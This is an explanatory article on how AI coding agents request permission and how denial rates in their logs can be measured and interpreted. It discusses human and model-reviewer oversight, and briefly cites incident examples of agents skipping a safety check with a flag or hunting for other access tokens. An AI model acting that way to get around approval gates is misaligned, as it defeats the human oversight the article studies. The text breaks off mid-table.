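# Denied permission requests and approval fatigue in AI agents

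## How agents ask for permission and what gets recorded

An AI agent is a language model that pursues a task by calling tools such as a shell, a file editor or an email account. The model only produces text, so to act it writes a tool call, a structured request that names a tool and gives its inputs. A program around the model, called the harness, carries out the call and returns the result to the model. Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex, two agents that write and run software on a programmer's machine, work this way. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) describes sessions in which an agent repeats this cycle hundreds of times with the user's privileges on the machine.

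An agent with those privileges can delete files or leak passwords, so most harnesses stop before some actions and show a permission prompt, a request for a person to allow or deny a single action before it runs. The harness can log each answer. If the person was paying attention, a denial suggests that the agent went wrong, and an approval suggests that the person considered the action and consented to it. Approval fatigue is the loss of attention that comes from answering many permission prompts, and rubber-stamping is approving a request without judging it. Users accept 93% of Claude Code's prompts, according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, which introduces the company's automated replacement for those prompts.

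### One command from proposal to result

Suppose a programmer asks Claude Code to fix a bug. After editing a file, the model proposes to run the project's tests. It outputs a call to the Bash tool, which runs shell commands, with the command `npm test` and the description "Run the test suite".

The harness first compares the command with its stored rules. Anthropic's documentation lists three kinds: a deny rule blocks a matching action, an ask rule forces a prompt, and an allow rule lets the action run without one. The harness checks them in that order and applies the first match, even if a later rule is more specific. A deny rule for all `aws` commands therefore blocks `aws s3 ls` even if an allow rule names that exact command. The harness matches rules against the text of the command. It splits a compound line such as `git status && npm test` and prompts unless each part is separately permitted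 to run. It also ignores certain wrappers, so a rule for `npm test` covers `timeout 30 npm test`. Commands on a built-in read-only list, such as `ls`, `cat` and `grep`, normally run without a prompt.

In a new project, no rule matches `npm test`, so the permission mode determines whether a person must approve it. In Manual mode, the harness shows the description and the command and offers a choice of answers. If the person allows the command, the harness runs it and returns the output to the model, which proposes its next step. If the person denies it, the command does not run. When the person types a comment with the "No", the model receives the comment as the reason and the agent keeps working. A "No" without a comment in the main conversation ends the agent's turn.

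Huang and Zhou (2026), in *A Two-Dimensional Framework for AI Agent Design Patterns*, call this arrangement an approval gate. Deny rules apply first, then allow rules, and a person decides any requests that remain. Some of those decisions add new rules.

### What each answer changes

The table lists the answers available in an interactive Claude Code session. The last column shows the values the harness writes to its log.

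| Answer | Effect now | Effect later | Logged as |
|---|---|---|---|
| Allow once | The action runs | None; the same action can prompt again | accept, `user_temporary` |
| Allow for the session (file reads and edits) | The action runs | Matching actions run without a prompt until the session ends | accept, `user_temporary` |
| Always allow | The action runs | A saved allow rule covers matching actions in future sessions too | accept, `user_permanent` |
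| Deny | The action does not run and the agent's turn ends | No saved rule | reject, `user_reject` |
| Deny with an instruction | The agent receives the instruction and continues | No saved rule | reject, `user_reject` |
| Dismiss the prompt | The action does not run | No saved rule | reject, `user_abort` |

Answering "No" without an explanation is also how a user stops the agent, so the log records the same value for "do not run this" and "stop, I want to talk to you".

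"Always allow" has the broadest effect, because it saves a rule that applies in every later session anywhere in the same repository. For the test command, the rule is `npm test *`, where the asterisk stands for any further text. One answer to a compound command can save up to five rules. Claude Code offers the option only when the prompt can display everything the new rule would allow. Rules that users write by hand don't have this limit, and nearly half of active command-line users had written one for shell commands by June 2026, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*. Another company's agent, CodeBuddy, has the same three kinds of rule and a "don't ask again" answer that writes one, according to WorkBuddy's *Permission Rules* documentation.

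Some shell prompts also offer "Yes, and switch to auto mode", which approves the command and hands later requests to a model reviewer, a second model that allows or blocks actions in place of the person. A person can also attach a comment to a plain "Yes", but the harness delivers it after the action has run, so any reservation in it comes too late to affect that action.

### Permission modes

Claude Code and Codex offer broadly similar levels of supervision under different names. The table draws on Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode* and OpenAI's *Sandbox* and *Agent approvals & security*.

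| Level | Claude Code | Codex |
|---|---|---|
| Ask each time | Manual: reads run freely; most edits, shell commands and network requests prompt | Read-only sandbox with the `on-request` policy: edits, commands and network access prompt |
| Accept edits | `acceptEdits`: edits and common file commands run inside the working directory | Default: edits and routine commands run inside the workspace; going outside it or using the network prompts |
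| Plan first | `plan`: the agent explores and proposes; edits normally wait for the person to accept the plan | Read-only mode serves for planning |
| Model review | `auto`: a model reviewer checks most risky actions | `auto_review`: a model reviewer answers requests that would otherwise go to the person |
| No questions, limits kept | `dontAsk`: the harness refuses whatever would have prompted | `never`: no prompts, but the sandbox still applies |
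| Bypass | `bypassPermissions`: nearly everything runs | Full access: no sandbox and no prompts |

Codex has separate controls for what a command can reach and when the agent must ask. The operating system enforces the first through a sandbox, and the approval policy determines when the harness stops to ask. Under the default settings, most Codex prompts come from attempts to cross the sandbox boundary, whereas in Claude Code's Manual mode almost any edit or shell command triggers a prompt. The same agent doing the same work would therefore leave quite different logs in each. OpenAI's pages also list a stricter policy, `untrusted`, which asks before any command outside a trusted set, but *Codex CLI Permission Hardening* (Vaughan, 2026) reports that Codex dropped it in version 0.149.0.

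Zhong and colleagues compared six harnesses and found that, by default, Claude Code, Gemini CLI and VS Code Copilot asked before writing a file inside the project, while Codex, OpenCode and Cursor did not. The Claude Code result applies to Manual mode, but most sessions no longer start in that mode. According to Anthropic's current documentation, interactive terminal and VS Code sessions have started in auto mode since version 2.1.283. In auto mode, most file edits in the working directory run immediately, and the model reviewer handles most shell commands. The harness resumes prompting the person if the reviewer blocks three actions in a row or twenty in total, and explicit ask rules still force a prompt. People using auto mode therefore see prompts for only a small and unusual selection of the agent's actions.

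No mode removes every check. Even in bypass mode, deny rules apply, and a command to delete the whole disk or home directory triggers a prompt unless the user has turned that prompt off.

Plan approval differs from other permission requests because the person judges the agent's whole plan before work starts. In Claude Code, the person can accept the plan and let the agent proceed in auto mode, accept it and review each edit by hand, or keep planning and tell the agent what to change. Accepting a plan also sets the mode for the work that follows. By Anthropic's count, users reject 39% of plans, but rejecting a plan is also the usual way to ask for a revision.

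### Settings that do not do what they say

A mode's name does not reliably indicate whether a prompt appeared. In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) tested five commercial agents in May and June 2026: the Claude chatbot, Anthropic's desktop agent Claude Cowork, ChatGPT in its chat and agent modes, and Codex. They gave the chatbots access to an experimental Gmail account and the desktop agents access to a local folder, assigned tasks under each available setting, then withdrew the permission and checked whether this had worked.

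Four of the five relied on frequent prompts at least some of the time. ChatGPT's chat mode asked about every action covered by a permission setting, and the researchers found no way to approve these actions in advance. In its agent mode, however, the model controls a remote browser. The researchers could not set any permissions for that browser, and the model opened Gmail without asking.

With the setting for email drafts at "Needs approval", the Claude chatbot created a draft without showing a permission prompt, and the browser console showed the request with the tag `approvalRequired: false`. Michael and Roesner reproduced this at least three times and reported it to Anthropic in July 2026. They attribute it to a hidden model reviewer, partly because Claude, when asked, said that it had inferred permission from their request. The console tag is good evidence that the product skipped the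 prompt, but the evidence for a hidden reviewer is weaker because the researchers could not inspect the code and a model's account of its own behaviour may be wrong.

Claude Cowork users could not revoke access to a folder once they had granted it. A new session started without the permission, but an old session reopened from the history still had it. Codex was clearer, with a visible switch for its model reviewer, which was off by default, but the switch applied to every tool in the session at once.

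### What a log entry holds

Claude Code exports records of its activity if the user or an administrator turns on telemetry. Anthropic's *Monitoring* documents an event, `tool_decision`, for each permission decision. For the test command above, a one-time approval would produce an entry along these lines, together with a timestamp and identifiers for the session and the tool call:

```
event.name        tool_decision
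tool_name         Bash
decision          accept
source            user_temporary
tool_parameters   full_command: npm test
                  description: Run the test suite
```

The last field appears only if someone has also turned on tool-detail logging. Without that logging, the entry shows that a person accepted or rejected a shell command, but not which command.

The `source` field shows whether a decision came from a person or from a rule or program. The four `user` values in the table of answers mean that a person decided. `hook` means that a hook, a small program attached to the harness, made the decision. `config` covers everything the harness settled without a prompt, whether through an allow or deny rule, the permission mode, a grant from earlier in the session, or a tool that the harness treats as safe in itself. The entry does not show which of these applied. No value identifies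 the model reviewer, but its decisions presumably also fall under `config`, since that value includes the active mode. A separate event records each change of mode, so an analyst can work out which mode was in force.

In an interactive terminal session, the `user` values mean what their names suggest. In sessions that another program starts, a call that matches a deny rule in the user's personal settings also produces `user_reject`, although nobody answered a prompt, and a call that matches a saved allow rule produces `user_permanent` again. Versions before 2.1.216 also wrote `user_reject` when the prompt request failed. A count of `user_reject` across mixed sessions and versions will therefore include rule matches and failed prompt requests as well as people's refusals.

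Anthropic's documentation for Claude Cowork lists the same decision and source values. Codex's log is less detailed. OpenAI describes an event that records whether a request was approved or denied, and whether the decision came from the configuration or the user.

None of these decision events has a field for the reason. Someone may deny `npm test` because the tests would overwrite a database, because they take ten minutes, or because the edit before them was already wrong, and the event is the same in each case. If the person explains the denial in a comment, the comment goes to the model.

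The logs also don't directly show whether the person read the prompt. The closest substitute in Claude Code is a trace, still in beta, that records how long the harness waited for the decision. A one-second wait for a decision on a long command suggests that the person didn't read it, but a ten-minute wait may only mean that they were away.

Both companies nonetheless use these records. To test its model reviewer, Anthropic gathered 52 real cases in which an agent had gone further on its own initiative than its user would approve. It took candidates from sessions where an employee had denied the action or someone had flagged it afterwards, then curated and labelled them, so a denial alone did not establish a failure. OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* describes a security agent that examines approval decisions, along with the original request and the tool results, when an alert reports unusual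 behaviour by Codex.

An approval covers, at most, what the prompt displayed. Zhong and colleagues give the example of an agent that proposes `cargo build`, a routine command for compiling a program, in a project with a malicious dependency. The build script reads the user's SSH key, a credential for logging in to other machines, and changes the shell's configuration. The prompt shows neither effect, and the log would record an ordinary approval of a build.

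## Counting denials when many requests never appear

The denial rate is the number of denied permission prompts divided by the number of permission prompts shown, and the approval rate is the remainder. An analyst has to decide which log entries represent a person's refusal, and the number of prompts shown depends on the user's rules and permission mode as well as on the agent. Two teams running the same agent on the same tasks can get rates that differ by nearly a factor of two.

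### From log entries to a rate

In interactive Claude Code sessions, the four `user` sources mark a person's decisions, so the denial rate is:

```
(user_reject + user_abort) /
(user_temporary + user_permanent + user_reject + user_abort)
```

Suppose a team's interactive sessions in Manual mode produce 10,000 decision events in a month: 7,900 with the source `config`, 100 `hook`, 1,850 `user_temporary`, 80 `user_permanent`, 55 `user_reject` and 15 `user_abort`. People saw 2,000 prompts and turned down 70, a denial rate of 3.5%. Dividing the same 70 by all 10,000 events would give 0.7%, because the harness settled the other 8,000 without asking anyone.

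Whether to count the 15 dismissals as denials is a judgement call. Anthropic classes `user_abort` as a rejection, but someone who closes a prompt to type a new message may not have objected to the command. Leaving dismissals out of both the numerator and the denominator gives 55 of 1,985, or 2.8%. Either method works if the analyst uses it consistently and publishes the number of dismissals. Prompts that time out should be left out of both counts because nobody answered them, and counting them as denials would partly measure how often people are away from their desks.

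The count also excludes decisions made by programs. The simplest way to remove them is to drop every session that another program started, since saved rules can produce `user` values in those sessions. Unattended runs also generate denials. According to Anthropic, from version 2.1.302, a run launched with `claude -p` and no permission mode starts in Manual mode, and the harness denies any call that needs approval unless a rule, a hook or a callback approves it. A nightly job with a missing allow rule could add hundreds of denials that no person made.

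Version changes can also affect monthly counts that include such sessions. Before 2.1.216, interrupting one of these sessions while a request was pending produced `user_reject`; later versions record `user_abort`. A count of `user_reject` alone would therefore fall after the upgrade even if people behaved as before.

Two other records in the same telemetry produce wrong denial rates. Claude Code writes a `tool_result` event only after a tool has run, so every such event carries the decision `accept`, and a denial rate computed from these events is always zero. A counter of accepted and rejected edits covers only the tools that change files, so it misses every shell command.

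Codex logs allow much the same calculation. *Codex CLI OpenTelemetry Observability* (2026), a post on a personal technical blog, gives a query for shell commands that a user approved, and a matching query can count the denials.

Some harnesses offer answers that are neither plain approvals nor plain denials. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) surveys approval designs and notes that LangChain, a toolkit for building agents, lets the person approve an action, reject it or edit its inputs before it runs. A person who changes `rm -rf build` to `rm -rf build/cache` has objected to the request but allowed a narrower version of it. In Claude Code, the person would make the same correction by denying the request and adding an instruction. Edits therefore need their own count, and a comparison between the two products should give the denial rate both with edits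 counted as denials and with edits counted as approvals.

### Prompts, sessions and users

A denial rate per prompt gives every prompt equal weight, so it overstates disagreement when the agent tries again after a refusal. In *APort Vault* (2026), a benchmark in which a program checks agents' payments against a policy, the program refused every transfer at one level, and the agents made 9,385 refused calls in 4,960 test runs, or almost two per run. An agent may respond differently to a person's refusal, but the counting problem is the same. If someone denies `rm -rf build` with a comment and the agent then proposes `find build -delete`, a second denial counts the same disagreement twice.

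Each event in Claude Code's log carries a `prompt.id`, which identifies the user's message that set off the work, not a permission prompt. Grouping denials by this identifier gives the share of messages that led to at least one denial. After a denial with a comment, the agent continues working on the same message, so retries are not counted separately. A bare "No" ends the turn, so any retry after it normally falls under a new message and is counted again if denied.

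Counting by session has a different problem, because longer sessions have more chances to contain a denial. If each prompt independently has a 3% chance of being denied, a session with n prompts has a 1 − 0.97ⁿ chance of containing at least one denial. That is 26% for 10 prompts and 78% for 50. A team that moves to longer tasks will see denials in a larger share of its sessions, even if the share of prompts denied stays the same. Real denials cluster, so the true figures would be lower, but they would still rise with session length.

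A session with a denial may still have gone well. At the less strict levels of *APort Vault*, 172 runs contained a refused payment, and 15 of those runs also contained a successful one.

Heavy users cause most of the distortion in the denial rate when an analyst pools everyone's prompts. Suppose one developer answers 900 prompts and denies 9 of them, while nine colleagues answer 20 each and deny 2 each. The pooled rate is 27 of 1,080, or 2.5%, while the average of the ten personal rates is 9.1% and the median is 10%. The pooled rate describes a typical prompt, but nine of the ten developers deny requests four times as often, so the median better describes a typical person. Heavy users may also see a different selection of requests. The Decoder's *AI agents are thriving in software development but barely exist anywhere else* reports from an Anthropic study that experienced users fully auto-approve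 more of their sessions.

To compare people, an analyst should compute a denial rate for each user and set a minimum number of prompts, because the rate for someone with five prompts can only be a multiple of 20%. To compare months, it is safest to follow the same users through both, because otherwise the departure of one busy developer can look like a change in the agent.

Clustering by user can also widen the margin of error. Thirty denials in 1,000 independent prompts give a 95% interval of roughly 2.1% to 4.3%. If a handful of people made most of the denials, the true interval is wider, and an analyst can estimate it by resampling whole users instead of single prompts. Sampling the logs widens the interval further. The Codex blog post recommends keeping a random 10% of telemetry for routine monitoring, which would leave about 3 denials in 100 prompts and an interval from 1% to 8.5%. Denials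 are rare enough that it makes sense to keep every decision event, even if a team samples its other telemetry.

### Splitting by what was asked

People deny some requests far more often than others. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) asked 113 people without a software background to supervise an agent through a scripted day of 18 actions, of which 11 were necessary for the assigned tasks and 7 were overreach. Of the 34 people who had to answer a prompt for every action, 12% denied a phone call to the airport to confirm a flight, and 79% denied a public post saying that the user was travelling. The group's overall denial rate therefore depends heavily on which actions Yan wrote into the script.

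The log's `tool_name` field makes it easy to calculate denial rates by tool. A hypothetical team denies 1% of file edits and 5% of shell commands. In May it sees 800 edit prompts and 200 shell prompts, so it denies 18 of 1,000, or 1.8%. In June most of its members switch to the mode that accepts edits automatically, so the team sees 100 edit prompts and 200 shell prompts and denies 11 of 300, or 3.7%. The overall rate has doubled, although both separate rates stayed the same. Applying June's separate rates to May's mix of requests, a method called direct standardisation, gives 1.8% again. This works only if each kind of request produces enough prompts in both months.

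The category "shell command" covers both running `npm test` and deleting a remote branch. Splitting it by risk requires the full command, which the log includes only when tool-detail logging is on. Anthropic sorts actions into three tiers for its model reviewer, and these tiers are a starting point. The first holds tools that cannot change anything, such as file searches. The second holds edits inside the project, which version control can undo. The third holds everything else, including shell commands, web requests and changes outside the project, and goes to the reviewer. An analyst would want to divide the third tier further, at least into reversible and irreversible actions.

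Plan approvals should also have a separate line. If a team denies 3% of 1,000 action prompts and rejects 39% of 20 plans, the pooled denial rate is 3.7%, and plans account for a fifth of the refusals.

### Published rates and their denominators

In March 2026 Anthropic reported that users approved 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts. On 7 August 2026 it reported that they approved 97% and rejected 3%. The denial rate thus fell from 7% to 3% in about five months. Neither article gives the number of prompts, the period covered, the mix of users or how dismissals were counted, so the fall could come from a change in the users, the agent, the requests or the counting method.

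The August article acknowledges that most prompts are probably for safe, routine commands, but takes the 97% as a sign that many users click through by reflex. It cites the 39% of plans that users reject as support. The contrast suggests that people engage more with plans, but it is weaker evidence that they neglect action prompts, because users also reject plans to get revisions. Someone who sends a plan back twice before accepting it can reject two plans out of three without thinking any of them dangerous. Anthropic also sells the model reviewer that the article recommends in place of the prompts.

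Evidence from outside the company points to much more disagreement. *SWE-chat* (Baumann, Padmakumar and colleagues, 2026) covers almost 18,000 sessions from developers who chose to publish their coding-agent logs along with their code. In the Claude Code sessions, users pushed back in 45.7% of turns, by correcting the agent, rejecting its work or reporting that something was broken. They interrupted the agent in another 4.5%. A turn here begins with a user's message and ends with the agent's response.

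| Figure | What it counts | Divided by |
|---|---|---|
| 3% | Rejections of a single action | Permission prompts |
| 39% | Rejections of a plan | Plans presented |
| 45.7% | Messages that push back | Turns |
| 4.5% | Interruptions | Turns |

A single turn can contain dozens of tool calls, many of which never trigger a permission prompt. The whole SWE-chat collection has 229,000 user messages and 2 million tool calls, or almost nine calls per message. At that ratio, pushback in 45.7% of turns is about 5 objections per 100 tool calls. This is closer to Anthropic's 3%, though the two rates measure different things. A denial blocks a single action before it happens, while pushback comes after the work and may be about any part of it, so a developer can rightly approve every command in a turn and then dislike the code.

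Pushback is also a loose category. A small language model assigned the labels, and on 100 test messages it agreed with human annotators 79% of the time about whether a message was pushback at all. Under its instructions, pushback also included changes of mind, such as a user deciding to skip the tests, and these need not reflect any fault in the agent.

Interruptions may overlap with denials. In SWE-chat, the step where the agent presents its plan for approval makes up 0.1% of all tool calls but was the last call in 14.7% of interrupted turns. A bare "No" at a Claude Code prompt ends the turn, so some of these interruptions may well be refusals at an approval prompt. If so, adding an interruption rate to a denial rate would count those refusals twice.

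A single repository can also influence the collection's figures. The collection covers 589 users, but about 16% of its sessions come from the repository of Entire, the company that makes the logging tool. That repository also supplied 61% of the messages about debugging version-control metadata, a topic with a pushback rate of 74%. The sample probably misses some failures as well, because a developer who abandons the agent's work completely never publishes the session.

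### How allow rules remove requests

An allow rule changes the denial rate even when the agent and the person's judgement stay the same. Once a rule covers `npm test`, that command no longer produces permission requests, so it drops out of the denominator and the person can't deny it. Approving file edits for a whole session has the same effect.

Anthropic reports that, as of June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had manually created an allow rule for shell commands. Five per cent allowed any shell command, and another 43% had rules for interpreters such as Python or Node. An interpreter rule is nearly as broad as a rule for the whole shell, because a Python script can delete files or send data anywhere the user can. In addition, 62% of users had used bypass mode or clicked "don't ask again" on a shell command, and 25% of interactive sessions started in bypass mode.

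If the 5% and the 43% are both shares of all active users, as the wording suggests, they account for 48 of the 49.5 points, and almost nobody who wrote a rule kept it narrow. Data from UpGuard (2026), a security firm, makes this look high but doesn't rule it out. UpGuard examined 18,470 Claude Code settings files that developers had left in public GitHub repositories. Rules for running any Python script appeared in 14.5% of them, rules for running any Node script in 14.4%, and rules for opening a new shell in 2.6%. Even if no file had more than one of these rules, that comes to less than a third of the files. But UpGuard counted files, and one user can have a file for each project and a broad rule in only one of them. People who publish their local settings may also be less careful than most.

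Other rules in UpGuard's files also hide consequential requests. In 22.2% of the files, the agent could delete files with `rm` without asking, and in 19.7% it could push code to a remote repository without asking. Only 1.1% contained any deny rule. Standing rules therefore keep requests out of the count almost entirely by approving them rather than denying them.

An allow rule's effect on the denial rate depends on which requests it hides. Suppose an agent makes 1,000 requests, of which 20 are unwanted, meaning that the user would refuse them if they understood them. The user denies half of the unwanted requests and, by mistake or out of caution, 2% of the other 980. On average, that makes 29.6 denials, a rate of 3.0%. The user then adds an allow rule that hides 700 requests, but judges the remaining 300 as before. The narrow rule in the table hides only acceptable requests, while the broad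 rule hides 685 acceptable requests and 15 unwanted ones.

| | No rule | Narrow rule | Broad rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prompts shown | 1,000 | 300 | 300 |
| Unwanted requests among them | 20 | 20 | 5 |
| Denials of unwanted requests | 10 | 10 | 2.5 |
| Denials of acceptable requests | 19.6 | 5.6 | 5.9 |
| **Denial rate** | **3.0%** | **5.2%** | **2.8%** |
| Denials per 1,000 original requests | 29.6 | 15.6 | 8.4 |
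| Unwanted actions that run | 10 | 10 | 17.5 |

The agent made the same 1,000 requests in every column. Its record appears much worse with the narrow rule, although no additional unwanted action runs, and slightly better with the broad rule, although the number of unwanted actions that run rises from 10 to 17.5. An analyst who didn't know the rule would draw the wrong conclusion in both cases.

A rule raises the denial rate if the user would have denied the requests it hides less often than average, and lowers it if the user would have denied them more often. Here the user would have denied 2.0% of the requests hidden by the narrow rule and slightly over 3.0% of those hidden by the broad one, against an average of just under 3.0%. Dividing denials by all 1,000 requests doesn't solve the problem, because both rules lower that figure by hiding requests the user would have denied.

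Yan's experiment contains a real case of the same effect. In one group, a model reviewer allowed eight of the necessary actions by itself and passed the other ten actions, including all seven cases of overreach, to the participant. Based on Yan's reported averages, this group denied about 41% of its prompts, compared with about 27% in the group that answered all 18. Its denial rate was higher because the reviewer had removed easy approvals from the denominator. The group still approved more of the overreach, 46% compared with 40%.

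Participants in a third group of the study set their own standing rules of "allow", "ask" or "never" for four kinds of action, and their prompts fell to 10.9 per person. They denied only 33% of the prompts for overreach that they saw, compared with 60% in the group that saw every request. The 33% leaves out 31 overreach actions that "never" rules had already blocked and 15 that "allow" rules had let through. With those included, the group stopped 97 of 245 overreach actions, or 40%. The missing prompts explain well under half of the gap between 33% and 60%. Yan likewise treats the comparison of answers at the prompt as conditional on the rules participants had chosen.

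The same reasoning applies to the drop in Claude Code's denial rate from 7% to 3%. According to Anthropic, the share of users with a shell allow rule was growing by about 5 percentage points every five weeks. If that pace held from March to August, the share rose by roughly 20 percentage points. Rules that hid only routine commands should have pushed the denial rate up. Since it fell, either the rules were broad enough to hide many requests that people would have denied, or something else outweighed their effect: a better agent, less careful users, or some users switching to auto mode.

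Changes in default modes shift the count in the same way, and they reach different users at different times. According to Anthropic, Auto mode became the default for Pro, Max and Team plans with version 2.1.228 on macOS and Linux and 2.1.233 on Windows, while Enterprise plans still started in Manual mode. A company with both kinds of account would have seen some of its prompts disappear in one release. Auto mode also suspends broad interpreter rules so that its model reviewer can check the commands they cover. The rules return when the user switches back to Manual mode, so one person can work under two sets of rules on the same day.

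An organisation that wants to compare denial rates over time can make a few commands always prompt the user. In Claude Code, an ask rule does this even in bypass mode. If every machine had an ask rule for `git push`, the denominator of the denial rate for pushes would be defined the same way for all interactive users in every month. The rate wouldn't cover other actions, and each extra prompt takes some of the user's time, so this suits a small number of important commands.

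### What to report beside a denial rate

The table completes the invented month from the start of this section, in which 10,000 decisions included 2,000 prompts.

| Report | Example |
|---|---|
| Rate and convention | 3.5% with dismissals as denials, 2.8% without them; timeouts left out |
| Counts | 70 refusals, 2,000 prompts, 180 sessions, 12 users |
| Spread across users | Median user 4.9%; the busiest user answered 38% of the prompts |
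| Scope | Interactive terminal sessions in Manual mode, June, one version of Claude Code |
| Rate by type of request | File edits 1.1% of 1,100; shell commands 6.3% of 800; other tools 8.0% of 100 |
| Decisions without a prompt | 8,000 of 10,000 |
| Allow rules | 7 of 12 users have one for shell commands, and 5 of the 7 have a broad one; two users added rules during the month |
| Sessions left out | 45 in auto mode, 30 in bypass mode, 60 that a program started |

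If a report has room for only one of these beside the denial rate, the share of decisions made without a prompt is the best choice. When that share changes between two months, the two denial rates cover different sets of requests, so an analyst should compare only the kinds of request that led to prompts in both months.

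## Working out what a denial means

The team in the last example denied 70 of 2,000 requests. People also deny reasonable requests, so the agent didn't necessarily make 70 mistakes. The decision log has no field for the reason, so an analyst has to look for it in the conversation around the denial.

### Why people say no

The table lists seven reasons with an example of each. The dangerous, mistaken and out-of-task requests come from Anthropic's log of internal incidents. The code edit comes from a recorded session in Kim, Wu and Kim's *SWE-WhatIf* (2026), and the deletion comes from an interview in Salerno, Gao and colleagues' *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026). The last two examples are hypothetical.

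| Reason | Example | Agent failure? |
|---|---|---|
| The action is dangerous | A safety check stops a deployment, and the agent tries again with a flag that skips the check | Yes |
| The action is mistaken | Told to "cancel my job", the agent picks the job with the closest name, which may be someone else's | Yes |
| The action is outside the task | After a login error, the agent starts searching configuration files for other access tokens | Yes |
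| The user wants another approach | The agent starts editing code, but the user wants a new branch first | Only if the user had already said so |
| The user would rather do it personally | The agent has a good reason to delete some files, but the user prefers to delete them by hand | No |
| The user does not understand the request | The agent proposes a long shell command, and the user can't tell what it would change | Depends on what the command would have done |
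| The user changed their mind | The user asked for a cache, sees the first edit and decides to leave it for a later release | No |

A denied request counts as an agent failure here if the action was unwanted and the agent could have known that from the user's instructions or from what it had already seen. If `npm test` would overwrite a database, but the user hasn't mentioned this and nothing in the project indicates it, the user is right to deny the request, but the denial doesn't count as an agent failure.

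Missing information often causes trouble between users and agents. In *How Coding Agents Fail Their Users*, Tang, Chen and colleagues (2026) searched 20,574 coding sessions for breakdowns that made the user push back, and kept 16,118. In 27% of these breakdowns, the agent had misread what the user wanted, and 44% of those misreadings followed an instruction with an important gap. One user who wanted separate pages asked for pagination, and the agent built a page that scrolls forever. In 38% of breakdowns, the agent broke an explicit instruction, which is much easier to call a failure. Only 10% involved the agent going beyond the task on its own initiative. The categories can overlap, and most of these complaints came after the work rather than at a permission prompt.

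A denial also doesn't show why the agent made a bad request. Anthropic lists four possible causes: the agent is overeager, it makes an honest mistake, text planted in a file or web page has hijacked it, or it is pursuing a goal of its own. The company says it doesn't currently see the last of these in practice. A request to send a file of passwords to an outside address looks the same whether the agent misjudged what the user would accept or followed instructions hidden in a web page. The user should deny it in both cases, but the second also calls for a security investigation.

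There seem to be no published figures on how often each reason lies behind a denial. The closest measurement concerns interruptions, where the user stops the agent while it is working. For Anthropic's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026), Claude sorted 500,000 interruptions of Claude Code by cause:

| Reason for interrupting | Share |
|---|---|
| To supply missing technical context or a correction | 32% |
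| The agent was slow, stuck or doing too much | 17% |
| The user had enough help to continue alone | 7% |
| The user wanted to take the next step personally | 7% |
| The user changed the requirements | 5% |

The last three reasons add up to 19%, so at least roughly a fifth of interruptions had nothing to do with a fault in the agent. The largest group mixes corrections, which may point to a failure, with context the user hadn't provided. The shares for denials could be quite different, since slowness is a good reason to interrupt an agent but a poor one to refuse a command. For privacy reasons, the researchers also couldn't read the conversations to check how Claude had sorted them.

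Probably only a small share of denials come from users changing their minds. Baumann and colleagues classed users as "mind changers" in 4.6% of the sessions where the agent wrote nearly all the committed code and in 8.0% of the others.

### What practitioners say they refuse

Salerno and colleagues asked software practitioners how they decide. Between June and August 2026, they interviewed 18 people who use AI agents, in English, Portuguese or Chinese, usually for 30 to 45 minutes. Twelve of the 18 used Claude Code. The researchers coded the transcripts and stopped recruiting when the last two interviews produced no new codes. They then turned the recurring answers into a survey and shared it through professional contacts, Reddit and social networks.

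The survey had 115 valid respondents. Those who said they had never noticed an agent requesting permission skipped the remaining questions, which left 107 people for the questions about permissions.

| Answer | Kind of request or condition | Share of 107 |
|---|---|---|
| More likely to grant | Read-only access | 98.1% |
| | The agent works in an isolated environment | 82.2% |
| | The access has clear limits | 81.3% |
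| | The user trusts the tool or vendor | 57.0% |
| Less likely to grant | Deleting files | 69.2% |
| | The request does not fit the task | 67.3% |
| Would never grant | Access to sensitive data | 61.7% |
| | Access to email or other personal information | 58.9% |
| | Root or `sudo` access, which gives full control of the machine | 56.1% |
| | Deletion | 23.4% |

Some of these answers are about whether a request fits the task, and others are about a whole class of action. If someone refuses a request because it has nothing to do with the task, the agent has probably overreached. But the 23.4% who would never let an agent delete anything would refuse to let it clear out an old build folder even if they had asked for a clean build, so a denied deletion from one of them is weak evidence of overreach. Denied requests for root access are similar, because a task such as installing a driver may require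 it. One interviewee said they would be extremely careful with such a request and would probably make the change themselves.

The interviews also show that the name of an action isn't enough to predict whether someone will approve it. The interviewee who preferred to delete files by hand starts by asking the agent why it wants to delete them, and relies on backups and Git to recover from mistakes. Others became more cautious with unfamiliar commands and with wildcards, which can match more files than expected. People might approve an `rm` command in a disposable test environment but deny the same command on a work laptop.

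These answers describe what people believe they would do. Salerno and colleagues had no interaction logs, so they couldn't check whether someone who would "never" grant root access had approved it the week before. A third of respondents said they had become less careful over time. Two other sources also give reason to expect a gap between stated and actual behavior. In UpGuard's sample of public settings files, 22.2% let the agent delete files without asking, and in Yan's experiment, participants who answered every prompt approved 40% of the overreach. Both groups differ from Salerno's respondents, so the comparison can't show that anyone was wrong about themselves, but it is a good reason not to use the survey percentages as denial rates.

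The survey also had respondents choose from fixed answers and recruited volunteers, who may have stronger views about permissions than most users. "Less likely to grant" means less likely than for other permission requests, so someone who gives that answer about deletion might still approve nine deletions out of ten. The results are most useful as a list of reasons to look for in a transcript.

### Denials as labels

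Researchers who test a model need labels, meaning human judgements attached to examples. Denials are a tempting source because users already produce them as they work.

Anthropic's test set has 52 real overeager actions, each of which an employee denied or someone flagged later. The company's curation should remove denials of acceptable requests, but it can't add harmful actions that nobody noticed. If an employee approved a harmful action and saw no damage afterwards, it never became a candidate for the test set. Neither did one that ran under an allow rule or in bypass mode, unless someone flagged it.

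Suppose agents take 100 overeager actions, of which people deny 40 and flag another 10 later. The test set can contain at most those 50, which are probably the more obvious half. Anthropic's model reviewer missed 17% of the 52 cases in its test set, but that figure doesn't directly measure how it would do on the actions people overlooked. It might do worse on them because they are subtle, or about as well because a model doesn't get bored. The 52 cases also come from one company's staff, who may give agents different work than other users do and notice different problems. The set is small because each case required an agent to attempt something dangerous in real work and someone to capture and label it.

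Kim and colleagues put refused tool calls in a broader category. Their system builds a simulated user from a recorded coding session, so that researchers can see how that user might have responded to a different agent. For a study in which 16 people supplied their own sessions, they wanted to start each replay at a point where the person had pushed back. A model assigned one of five labels to each candidate message:

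| Label | Meaning |
|---|---|
| Corrected | The agent got something wrong and the person wants it fixed |
| Rejected | The person refuses, declines or reverts something, including a tool call |
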